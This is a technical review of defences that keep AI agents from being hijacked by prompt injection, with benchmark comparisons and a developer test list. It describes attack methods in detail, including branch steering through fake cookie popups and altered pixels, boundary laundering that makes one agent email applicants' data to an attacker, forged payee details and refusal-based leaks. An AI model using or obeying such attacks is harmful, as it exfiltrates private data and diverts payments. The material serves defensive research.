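Take two starting points that differ only in data that some observer may not see, and run the same program from each. Let `μ(q)` be the probability that the observer ends up seeing result `q` from the first starting point, and `ν(q)` the probability from the second. A run that stops early or never finishes produces no result, so each set of probabilities may add up to less than 1. The theorem says that a third set of probabilities, `ω`, always exists such that:

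```
μ(q) ≤ ω(q)   and   ν(q) ≤ ω(q)   for every result q
sum of all ω(q)  ≤  1
```

In other words, the two sets could become equal if more of the unfinished runs had finished. Some invented numbers show what this allows:

| | "Done" | "Sorry" | No result | Allowed? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| First secret | 60% | 0% | 40% | Yes: `ω` can be 60% and 40%, which adds up to 100%. |
| Second secret | 50% | 40% | 10% | |
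| First secret | 60% | 0% | 40% | No: `ω` would need 60% and 60%, which adds up to 120%. |
| Second secret | 0% | 60% | 40% | |

If every run finishes, the two sets of probabilities are identical, and the observer learns nothing. Otherwise, the statistical distance between them (half the sum of the absolute differences) is at most the average share of unfinished runs. In the allowed example, both figures are 25%, so this program leaks the maximum possible under the theorem.

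The result applies to every program in the language, including agents that generate code and run it partway through. Garby and colleagues checked the proof by machine in Lean, a language for writing programs and proofs about them. They also proved that the interpreter that runs the agents and calls the model follows the rules in the theorem.

This rules out a class of tracking errors. For example, Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's interpreter treated an untrusted value as trusted once it was inserted into a string literal. A plan that put Bob's forged address into a string before sending the email would have accidentally marked the address as trusted.

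A second theorem guarantees that the `endorse` operation can't leak a secret, whatever untrusted text the attacker supplies. It doesn't guarantee integrity, because the purpose of `endorse` is to change it.

#### The limits of the theorem

The theorem doesn't cover information leaked by whether a run finishes. It also treats all data sources as part of the program, while a real agent calls outside services that can change between calls. Garby and colleagues name this as a limitation. They also rely on the developer to label the sources correctly and put a check at every sink.

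Endorsement let through the two attacks that succeeded against their agent. In both, the user had asked the agent to read a text file and make the payment described there, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. The planner had endorsed those contents in its plan before seeing them. Without `endorse`, the executor blocks the payment whether or not the file is genuine, because the genuine text and the attacker's carry the same label, as with Alice's email. The harness can restrict which endorsements a planner may write, but the agent then can't complete some of these tasks.

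### Branch steering

A plan can contain a harmful branch from the start, and the attacker then only has to get the agent to take it. Garby and colleagues saw this in a run of CaMeL with its policies switched off. The user asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions. The planner, which couldn't see the file, wrote a loop with one branch for each available tool, and the file's contents determined which branches ran. Whoever wrote the file could therefore call any tool without changing the plan.

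Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) studied the problem in computer-use agents, which view a screen and then click and type, and named it branch steering. They adapted CaMeL to these agents. The planner writes the whole plan before any model views the screen. During the run, a quarantined vision model describes the screen, a second check compares the description with a prediction such as "a cookie banner is visible", and the yes-or-no result selects a branch of the plan.

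Screens are unpredictable, so these plans need far more branches than plans for agents with ordinary tools. The average plan had 39.7 branches and 41.1 tool calls, compared with 3.7 and 4.9 for CaMeL's plans on AgentDojo. About half of each plan was fallbacks that never ran. On OSWorld, a benchmark of everyday computer tasks, the design kept up to 57% of the performance of frontier models and improved smaller open models by up to 19%. An injected instruction can't add a step to such a plan, but a false observation at any branch can change which of the planned steps run.

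Foerster and colleagues built two attacks:

- **A fake cookie popup.** Many plans begin by finding and dismissing any cookie popup. The attacker puts an imitation inside an advertisement, and the agent clicks it and lands on the attacker's site. Variants pass through harmless sites first, or put the popup on a page that the agent will reach later.
- **Altered pixels.** The attacker makes small, calculated changes to an advertisement's image. The vision model then returns the wrong place to click, along with a plausible explanation.

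The attacker has to control part of what appears on the screen and guess roughly what the plan contains. Buying an advertisement may be enough for the first. Foerster and colleagues assume an attacker who knows the task and the available tools. Handling a cookie popup is such a routine step that it is easy to guess.

Labels are much less useful for clicks than for email. A call to `send_email` has a recipient that the gate can check, but `click(412, 300)` could close a window or delete a file, depending on what is at that point. The coordinates always come from the screen, so a rule against tainted coordinates would block every click. Foerster and colleagues left such policies out of their tests for this reason.

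One proposed cross-check compares the vision model's answer with the page's underlying structure, the DOM. Another uses an independent vision model to check whether the answer fits the screenshot and the instruction. Both add work to each step, and neither is guaranteed to catch an attack. An attacker who supplies part of the page also writes that part of the DOM, which is how the fake popup gets past the first check. The altered pixels are meant to get past the second by making the original vision model return an answer that a verifier would expect. The second check relies on an image that fools one model usually failing to fool a different one.

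Some deterministic checks remain possible. The agent's network proxy can still block the attacker's site if it checks every page the agent reaches, not just the first link. For agents with ordinary tools, a developer can also test a plan's branches the same way as a list of options, allowing only those that would be acceptable if an attacker chose them. The loop with a branch for every tool would fail this test.

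### When one agent's output becomes another's request

Larger systems often divide work among several agents. A coordinating agent receives the user's request and passes parts of it to specialists, and each specialist treats the coordinator as its user. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) shows that such a system can be vulnerable even if every agent runs CaMeL.

In their example, the user asks for a summary of job applicants' details to be sent to Julie on Slack. The coordinator's plan is roughly this:

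```
raw     = database_agent("Get all the job applicant information.")
summary = quarantined_model("Summarise this.", raw)
notification_agent("Send this summary to Julie via Slack: " + summary)
```

An attacker has put an instruction in the database to send the data to `ruth@email.com` as well. The database agent and the coordinator both keep that text in variables, so their planners never read it and their plans don't change. The third line joins the summary to the coordinator's own words. The notification agent receives the result as its user's request, so its planner reads all of it and writes a plan that sends the Slack message and also emails the applicants' details to Ruth. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering.

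These tests ran with CaMeL's policies switched off, but a rule that recipients must be trusted wouldn't have helped. The notification agent's planner copies Ruth's address from the user's request into its plan as a literal, so its executor labels the address trusted. Bob's forged address would become trusted in the same way if the coordinator wrote "Send the budget to" followed by the address from the notes.

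The attacker only needs to control some data that the first agent reads, provided that an agent in the system pastes tool results into its requests to other agents. This is the most natural way to write such requests. Peters-Gill and colleagues argue that, under mild assumptions about what the agents can do, any such system with more than one agent and at least one untrusted tool lets untrusted data change its overall sequence of calls.

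Protecting each agent separately still stops some attacks. In another setup, an attacker used injected text to try to make a database agent read a private database. The attack failed in all five trials because it required that agent's own planner to follow the text.

#### A separate channel for data

Their repair, multi-CaMeL, splits each request in two. The instruction travels as text that the receiving planner may read, and values from untrusted data travel beside it as variables with their labels:

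```
notification_agent("Send the attached summary to Julie via Slack.", data=summary)
```

The notification agent's planner can pass `summary` to a tool but can't read it. Peters-Gill and colleagues tested the design on MultiAgentDojo, their extension of AgentDojo to multi-agent systems.

| System | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|
| No CaMeL | 12.9% |
| CaMeL in each agent separately | 0.2% |
| Multi-CaMeL | 0.0% |

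The last two rows are so close that the benchmark gives little evidence of how much the extra channel adds. The worked attack is better evidence of the flaw, because it is designed to get through agents that are protected separately, and an attacker who knew the system would choose something like it.

Multi-CaMeL completes fewer tasks, because a specialist can't adapt its plan to data that its planner can't see. Across the five models tested, the loss was smaller for more capable models and modest for the strongest. A developer who can't change how the agents communicate could instead give each incoming request the labels of everything in it. This is also safe, but a single untrusted value would taint the specialist's whole context and block its guarded tools.

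### Harm through text alone

Narisetty and colleagues distinguish an agent that says something harmful from one that does something harmful, and point out that these defences deal only with harmful actions. An email to the right person can still do damage through its content.

Suppose the user asks the agent to send Bob a summary of the meeting, and an attacker has added a line to the notes saying that a supplier has a new bank account. The user supplied Bob's address, and Bob may read the notes, so the email satisfies both of the gate's rules. Bob then pays the wrong account himself, and the user's executor can't block the payment. He may be less suspicious than if he had read the notes, because the message came from a colleague. If Bob has an agent that trusts mail from colleagues, the false account number reaches it with a trusted label, just as Ruth's address did.

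The attacker only needs to add text to something that the agent will summarise. Requiring a trusted message body would prevent the attack, but it would also block most useful email. A milder measure is for the executor to add a line naming the source, such as "Summarised from meeting notes that people outside the company can edit." The labels already contain this information. But the quarantined model may have blended several sources into one paragraph, and the executor can then list the sources but can't match each sentence to its source. Readers would also soon start skipping a notice that appeared on every message.

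An attack can also target the user. An answer such as "Bob has a new address, so please update your contacts" contains no tool call for the executor to block. If the user saves the address by hand, the executor will treat it as trusted from then on. The application can at least display untrusted text in a marked block with its source, separate from the agent's own words and from any approval dialog. This depends on the user reading the mark, and it doesn't help if the planner has read the text and paraphrases the claim.

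One of AgentDojo's travel attacks falls into this category. The attacker's text is in a hotel review, and the benchmark counts the attack as successful if certain words appear in the agent's answer. According to Garby and colleagues, it was one of only two attacks that succeeded against CaMeL in its designers' tests, and it succeeded because the agent quoted the reviews word for word. FIDES's designers set the same attack aside as outside the scope of their policies. A user who sees the attacker's text as one guest's opinion can discount it, but has less reason to if the agent presents it as its own recommendation.

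## Testing the gate and measuring its cost

Researchers test these executors by planting attacks and counting how many succeed, and by giving the agent ordinary tasks and counting how many it still completes. Most published figures come from one benchmark, AgentDojo. The figures vary widely with the model, the rules and what happens after the executor blocks a call.

### AgentDojo and WASP

AgentDojo has 97 user tasks, such as paying the bill in a named file, across four settings (office, travel, banking and chat). According to *AgentDyn*, an agent has about 20 tools and needs three or four steps for a typical task.

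A separate set of injection tasks describes what an attacker wants, such as a payment to the attacker's account. The tester pairs each user task with each injection task from the same setting and plants the attacker's instruction in data that the agent will read. After the run, ordinary code checks whether the agent completed the user's task and whether it carried out the attacker's. This gives two figures:

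```
task completion rate  =  user tasks completed / all user tasks
attack success rate   =  attacked runs in which the attacker's goal happened / all attacked runs
```

AgentDojo's automatic checks for successful attacks make mistakes. They counted three successes against FIDES with its policies on, but Costa and colleagues inspected all three and decided that none should count. Across all the agents they tested, AgentDojo had sometimes counted a call that the gate had blocked, an action that the policy allowed, or an attack that had changed only the agent's text.

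WASP tests agents that use a web browser. It combines 21 attacker goals on copies of GitLab and Reddit with two user tasks, posting a comment and upvoting a post. The attacker's instruction is either in the page's text or in a link's address, which makes 84 cases. Kolluri and colleagues counted an attack as successful if it diverted the agent from the user's task, even if it didn't achieve the attacker's goal.

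### Counting approvals as well as tasks

An executor that refuses every call has an attack success rate of zero. Costa and colleagues tested something close to this, a planner that never sees untrusted data and has no quarantined model to read it. They counted no successful attacks, even with the gate off, but the planner completed only 47.5% of the office tasks, compared with 75.0% for an unprotected agent.

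The completion rate can also make an executor look worse than it is, because a person could approve many of the calls it refuses. Kolluri and colleagues therefore count these approvals, using two measures. The human-in-the-loop load (HITL load) is the total number of approvals needed for the tasks that the agent completes. TCR@k is the share of all tasks that it completes with at most `k` approvals each:

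```
v(task)  =  number of calls in the run that fail the gate
load     =  sum of v(task) over the completed tasks
TCR@k    =  completed tasks with v(task) ≤ k / all tasks
```

Suppose an agent attempts five tasks:

| Task | Completed? | Calls that failed the gate | Added to the load |
|---|---|---|---|
| Send Ana tomorrow's schedule | Yes | 0 | 0 |
| Summarise the meeting notes | Yes | 0 | 0 |
| Send Bob the document he asked for | Yes | 1 | 1 |
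| Pay three invoices | Yes | 3 | 3 |
| Do what an email asks | No | 6 | 0 |

The load is 4. Two of the five tasks needed no approval, so TCR@0 is 40%. Allowing one approval per task also completes the task with Bob's email and raises the rate to 60%. Allowing three completes the invoice task and raises it to 80%. The rate can't go higher because no number of approvals completes the last task.

The user in this example could have seen ten prompts instead of four. Kolluri and colleagues leave out failed tasks because a person would probably notice that the agent was making no progress and stop it. In most of their failed runs, the agent kept attempting calls that the gate rejected. A developer who wants to know how often the agent will interrupt people would need to count the prompts from failed tasks too.

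The load can fall simply because an agent fails more of the difficult tasks, so it needs to be read alongside the completion rate. It also counts every prompt equally, although endorsing a long email takes far more reading than approving one address.

Both measures also assume a perfect reviewer. In their measurements without attacks, Kolluri and colleagues assumed that a person would approve every call in a completed task. For attacks on AgentDojo, they assumed that the person would stop every malicious call sent for review. No attack can succeed under that assumption, so their result of zero successful attacks on AgentDojo doesn't measure how people behave. By contrast, most of Anthropic's paid testers approved a clearly dangerous command.

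### FIDES and the cost of the gate

Costa and colleagues counted 152 successful attacks against an unprotected GPT-4o agent, after removing misjudged ones. FIDES with its policies off allowed 21, because its planner could still read hidden variables. With the policies on, no attacks succeeded against any agent they tested, including the basic one, so the choice of agent mainly affected how much work got done.

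| Tasks completed without attacks (GPT-4o) | Office | Travel | Banking | Chat |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic agent, policies off | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Basic agent, policies on | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, policies off | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% |
| FIDES, policies on | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

Costa and colleagues report that FIDES completes 8% more tasks than a basic agent. This compares the two agents with policies on, when FIDES completes an average of 50.0% of tasks across the four settings and the basic agent 41.9%. The unprotected agent averages 84.3%. Hiding untrusted data recovers some of the tasks lost to the gate, but with GPT-4o most of the loss remained.

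The travel tasks are an exception. Many of them use tools that the policies allow even in an untrusted context, so the basic agent lost nothing, while GPT-4o often misused FIDES's variables. OpenAI's reasoning model o1 handled the variables better and raised FIDES's score on travel from 41% to 68%. With o1, FIDES's average advantage over the basic agent grew to 16%.

The zero applies to injected calls. It doesn't cover swapped values such as a forged payee, which the tested policies didn't check.

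### PRUDENTIA and the number of approvals

PRUDENTIA, the version of FIDES whose planner is given the rules, was tested on AgentDojo with four models. Each cell below gives TCR@0, then the load. The basic agent refers every consequential call to a person, while the others refer only calls that fail the gate.

| Model | Basic agent | Basic agent with gate | FIDES | PRUDENTIA |
|---|---|---|---|---|
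| GPT-4o | 28.0%, 59.4 | 38.4%, 39.4 | 50.3%, 7.8 | 42.5%, 23.8 |
| o3-mini | 24.3%, 48.2 | 35.5%, 32.4 | 50.1%, 18.8 | 59.1%, 16.4 |
| o4-mini | 32.8%, 48.6 | 42.5%, 34.6 | 53.2%, 36.8 | 59.4%, 19.2 |
| GPT-5 | 35.1%, 52.0 | 43.4%, 40.4 | 57.1%, 41.3 | 72.7%, 7.3 |

The first two columns isolate the benefit of labels. With o3-mini, both versions of the basic agent eventually completed 62.5% of tasks, but the gate reduced the number of approvals by a third because it could allow many calls without one. PRUDENTIA did best with GPT-5, completing 72.7% of tasks with no approvals and 80.0% with unlimited approvals, and it needed only 7.3 approvals across the whole benchmark.

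These figures come from the paper's appendix, and some comparisons in its main text don't match them:

- After discussing o3-mini, the text puts the gain in TCR@0 at 9.7 points from adding the gate and a further 10.7 from FIDES. Those are the gains for o4-mini. For o3-mini they are 11.2 and 14.6.
- Kolluri and colleagues write that the gate and FIDES cut the load by a factor of 1.5 to 2.6. This holds for o3-mini, but the factors for o4-mini are only 1.4 and 1.3.
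- They also write that PRUDENTIA consistently needs fewer approvals than the other agents. With GPT-4o it needed three times as many as FIDES and completed fewer tasks without help.
- The largest improvement over FIDES that they mention is a factor of 1.9, but with GPT-5 it was 5.7.

The result for GPT-4o suggests that giving a planner the rules helps only if the model can plan around them. Developers using a small or old model should compare both designs before choosing PRUDENTIA.

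On WASP, attacks diverted the basic agent in 14.6% to 61.1% of cases, depending on the model and the site. None diverted PRUDENTIA, which needed no approvals and completed at least as many tasks as the basic agent in every comparison. With o3-mini on Reddit, completion rose from 25.0% to 58.3%, because the injected text no longer distracted the planner. But WASP tests the easiest kind of task for an executor, because an agent can upvote a post or leave a comment without reading anything other users wrote. Kolluri and colleagues expected FIDES to do about as well.

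#### Tokens and money

The extra model calls cost money. With GPT-4o, Kolluri and colleagues estimated the average cost of an AgentDojo task at 0.4 to 1.1 US cents for the basic agent with a gate, 1.5 to 3.3 cents for FIDES and 3.9 to 6.3 cents for PRUDENTIA. On the banking tasks, which were the shortest, PRUDENTIA cost about ten times as much as the basic agent. Much of this cost comes from its long instructions, and the researchers hadn't yet tried to reduce it.

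Checking labels adds almost nothing to these costs, which come from the quarantined model's answers, the planner's longer instructions and the extra turns. With o3-mini, the basic agent averaged 2.0 turns per banking task, FIDES 2.4 and PRUDENTIA 4.9. CaMeL uses 2.8 times as many input tokens and 2.7 times as many output tokens as an unprotected agent, according to figures that Narisetty and colleagues cite.

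### CaMeL and LLMbda

Narisetty and colleagues also cite CaMeL, which completed 77% of AgentDojo's tasks under attack, compared with 84% for an unprotected agent. No attack within CaMeL's threat model succeeded. The 7-point gap suggests a much smaller loss than FIDES had with GPT-4o, but CaMeL's figure was measured with o3, a stronger model.

Garby and colleagues found a larger loss when they ran CaMeL themselves. They compared it with their own LLMbda agent on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, with nine attacks per task and three repetitions. The attack counts below include only completed runs.

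| Agent | Model | Tasks completed without attacks | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| LLMbda | GPT-5.2 | 75.0% | 2 of 432 |
| | Qwen3.7-plus | 75.0% | 0 of 432 |
| | MiMo-v2.5 | 64.6% | 0 of 432 |
| CaMeL, policies off | GPT-5.2 | 66.7% | 1 of 240 |
| | MiMo-v2.5 | 70.8% | 4 of 382 |
| CaMeL, policies on | GPT-5.2 | 37.5% | 0 of 231 |
| | MiMo-v2.5 | 37.5% | 0 of 357 |

Across the three models, two of 1,296 attacks on LLMbda succeeded, both involving the replaced payment file that its planner had endorsed.

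Turning on CaMeL's policies roughly halved the number of tasks it completed. The same happened to TypeGuard, a system written in Haskell with comparable rules. On AgentDojo's chat tasks, TypeGuard completed 15 of 21 with its policies off and 8 with them on. CaMeL completed 7 with its policies on under the same conditions.

LLMbda kept its checks on throughout, but it enforced only a subset of CaMeL's policies, and its planner could endorse untrusted data in advance. Without endorsement, its completion rate fell to 62.5% with Qwen3.7-plus and 54.2% with MiMo-v2.5. Both rates are well above CaMeL's 37.5%, but the difference in policies may explain part of the gap. The uncertainty is also large because there were only 16 tasks. The 95% interval for CaMeL's rate extends 26.6 percentage points either way.

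#### What stopped the attacks

With its policies off, CaMeL allowed five successful attacks in 622 completed runs. The gate therefore had very few attacks left to stop, but it still prevented a lot of ordinary work.

Garby and colleagues explain why by sorting the 144 pairs of tasks and attacks into two categories. In 97 pairs, the attack needs a tool call or file that the plan for the user's task would never include. For example, a plan for summarizing recent payments has no step that sends money. Writing the plan before reading any untrusted data is normally enough to stop these attacks. In the other 47 pairs, the plan itself could serve the attacker's purpose.

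Bob's forged address belongs to the second category, since the plan already includes the email the attacker wants to redirect. Results for that category are much more informative about the gate than the overall rate is, but they rest on few distinct cases. LLMbda blocked all 141 attacks in this category with Qwen3.7-plus, but these were 47 pairs run three times each, and the 95% interval for its true resistance rate starts at 92.4%.

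### Why the percentages don't compare

CaMeL scores 77% in one account and 37.5% in another, and neither figure has to be wrong. Results from different papers can differ for several reasons that have little to do with the executor:

- **The model.** The unprotected agent in CaMeL's comparison completed 84% of tasks. Kolluri and colleagues' basic agent completed between 62.5% and 72.3%, even with unlimited approvals.
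- **The tasks.** Some papers use all four settings and others use only one. The number of attacks also varies. Narisetty and colleagues count 629 cases in AgentDojo, while Garby and colleagues cite another system's results on 963.
- **The labels and policies.** AgentDojo comes with neither, so each team writes its own. A lenient policy raises the completion rate, and AgentDojo's attacks may not reveal what it lets through.
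- **Approvals.** Kolluri and colleagues point out that earlier papers gave TCR@0 for the protected agent but compared it with an unprotected agent that could do anything, as if a person had approved every call.

The most informative comparisons are those within a single paper where only one thing changes, such as whether the gate is on, while the agent, model and tasks stay the same.

### Attacks that adapt to the defence

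AgentDojo's attacks are fixed texts, and most are older than the defences that researchers test on them. A developer can adjust a defence until it stops these texts without making it any better at stopping new attacks. Nasr and colleagues showed how misleading tests on fixed attacks had been for defences that rely on a model.

Ma and colleagues built AutoDojo to generate new attacks automatically. It starts with known injections and scores each by how many user requests it hijacks. A language model uses the scores to suggest why the weaker injections failed, then writes a new one. AutoDojo tests that injection on the protected agent, adds it to the list and repeats this a few times. The attacker sees only how often each injection succeeds and doesn't know which defence is in place.

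Even this limited attacker did much better than the fixed attacks. PIGuard, a classifier for detecting injections, had blocked every fixed attack on an agent using GPT-4o-mini, but AutoDojo's attacks succeeded 28.0% of the time. Five defences had kept the success rate of fixed attacks near zero on that agent, and AutoDojo got through all of them except Progent.

#### A small test of Progent

Progent checks permissions and doesn't track taint. A language model writes rules about which tools the agent may use and with which arguments, and ordinary code checks every call against them. The model can also update the rules as the agent works, so an attacker might use text in a tool's result to get the model to allow a harmful call.

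Narisetty and colleagues wrote an attack for this purpose that presented the harmful action as a necessary step someone had already authorised. They tested it three times with Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, on eight user tasks from each of three AgentDojo settings.

| Attack success rate | No defence | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adapted attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
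| Chat | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Office | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Average | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |

The adapted attack did worse on average than the standard one. Progent may have resisted it, but Narisetty and colleagues suggest that its gentler wording also made the agent less likely to obey. The office tasks can't be used to judge Progent, because the small model ignored the planted instructions even without a defence. With Progent, average task completion under attack fell from 45.2% to 27.1%, and each task took about 15 times as many model calls.

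The researchers describe these results as preliminary and not peer reviewed, and their company builds security tools of this type. They didn't test an attack that uses only calls the rules already allow. Bob's forged address is such an attack, and it would pass if Progent's rules let the agent email any address.

Narisetty and colleagues propose a fuller test in which an attacker who knows the policy targets each part of the defence. The attacker would try to make untrusted data look trusted, persuade the user to endorse it and learn secrets from refusals. The test would measure attack success, completed tasks, overhead and how often the agent asks for endorsement. The researchers found no independent evaluation of this kind for taint-tracking executors such as CaMeL and FIDES.

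#### Attacks without injected instructions

In *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026) designed privacy attacks that look like ordinary requests. In one, an outsider shares a page that mixes real private records with invented ones and asks the agent to clean it up. A cautious agent refuses to delete some entries, and its refusals reveal which records are real.

On live Gmail and Notion accounts, this attack leaked 34.7% of the private items when a model-based privacy checker protected the agent, and none when FlowSeal did. FlowSeal, the researchers' own system, labels records by owner and checks every call that writes or shares data. Across all their tests, it leaked at most 3.3% of items and completed 72.4% of harmless tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best alternative.

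FlowSeal is only partly deterministic. Ordinary code decides when to run a check, but a separate language model compares the outgoing text with the protected records. Shim and colleagues left prompt injection out of their threat model, so these results complement the AgentDojo figures but can't replace them.

#### Harder ordinary work

AgentDyn addresses the opposite weakness in AgentDojo, which is that its ordinary tasks are too easy to plan. AgentDyn counts only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks as requiring the agent to change its plan partway through. Costa and colleagues classify about 20 as data-dependent, a similar category, so the number depends on the definition.

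AgentDyn has 60 tasks, which take an average of 7.1 steps. All of them require replanning, and each includes a helpful third-party instruction that the agent has to follow. CaMeL completed far fewer of these tasks because it can't change its first plan. Progent's results also dropped sharply, since writing accurate permissions is harder with more tools.

An executor that never lets outside text influence the plan will do badly on a benchmark made entirely of tasks that require it. Real work probably includes tasks of both kinds, but neither AgentDyn nor AgentDojo measures the proportions. AgentDyn uses one of AgentDojo's fixed attacks by default, so it is a harder test of usefulness than AgentDojo but not of security.

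### Newer models

Many of these figures come from old models. FIDES's results are for GPT-4o and o1, both from 2024, and AgentDyn's main comparison of defences also used GPT-4o. PRUDENTIA's best results came with GPT-5, released in August 2025. The most recent models in the AgentDojo tests of taint-tracking executors are the three that Garby and colleagues used in 2026.

Newer models should complete more tasks under the same rules, as the results for o1 and GPT-5 suggest. They may also obey fewer injections. Shim and colleagues cite OpenAI's claim that GPT-5.6 Sol had one-sixth as many prompt-injection failures as a model from four months earlier. An executor would then seem to prevent fewer attacks on a benchmark of planted instructions, but it would still be needed to block swapped values such as Bob's forged address.

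### A test list for developers

A developer can test most of an executor without a language model by replacing the planner with a short script that proposes the calls that need checking. The test then doesn't depend on whether an injection fools a model, and each case needs only one run because the gate is deterministic.

**1. Send a tainted value to every sink.** The value should look ordinary, like Bob's forged address, and it should arrive by every route that the agent supports:

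```
for each guarded argument of each tool:
    for each route:  direct copy, joined strings, text template, quarantined model,
                     saved memory, request from another agent
        send a tainted value by that route             expect: refusal
        send the same value from a trusted source      expect: the call runs
```

The second call confirms that the gate refused the first because of its label. Testing the text-template route would have exposed the error in CaMeL's interpreter that labeled untrusted values as trusted. If a plan can branch, the developer should run each test with the branch taken and not taken, because a default value may wrongly keep a trusted label.

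**2. Removing the labels.** The developer removes the label from one source at a time and repeats the first test. The executor should treat that source's data as untrusted and private, or refuse to start. This test should also be run when adding a tool, since a new tool is the most likely to lack a label.

**3. Altering an approved call.** After approving the email to Bob, the developer changes one character of the address, replaces the contents of `budget.pdf` without renaming the file, or submits the approved call twice. Each of these actions should trigger a new prompt. The developer should also check that a very long address or file name can't push the recipient out of view.

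**4. Repeated refusals.** The developer prepares two copies of the test data that differ only in one secret, such as whether a file exists or who may read it. The script then makes the same forbidden calls on both. Everything the planner or an outsider can see should match, including error messages and which later calls succeed. If anything differs, the developer should count how many attempts the executor allows before it stops. Shim and colleagues' mix of real and invented records is a useful extra case.

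**5. Counting prompts on ordinary work.** This test runs the real planner on a sample of actual user requests, with no attacks. The developer records completed tasks, prompts and cost per task, with the gate on and off. The developer should also count prompts from failed tasks, which the HITL load omits, and record which rule caused each prompt. If most prompts come from a single rule, such as one that blocks every new recipient, a trusted address book may remove more of them than a better model would.
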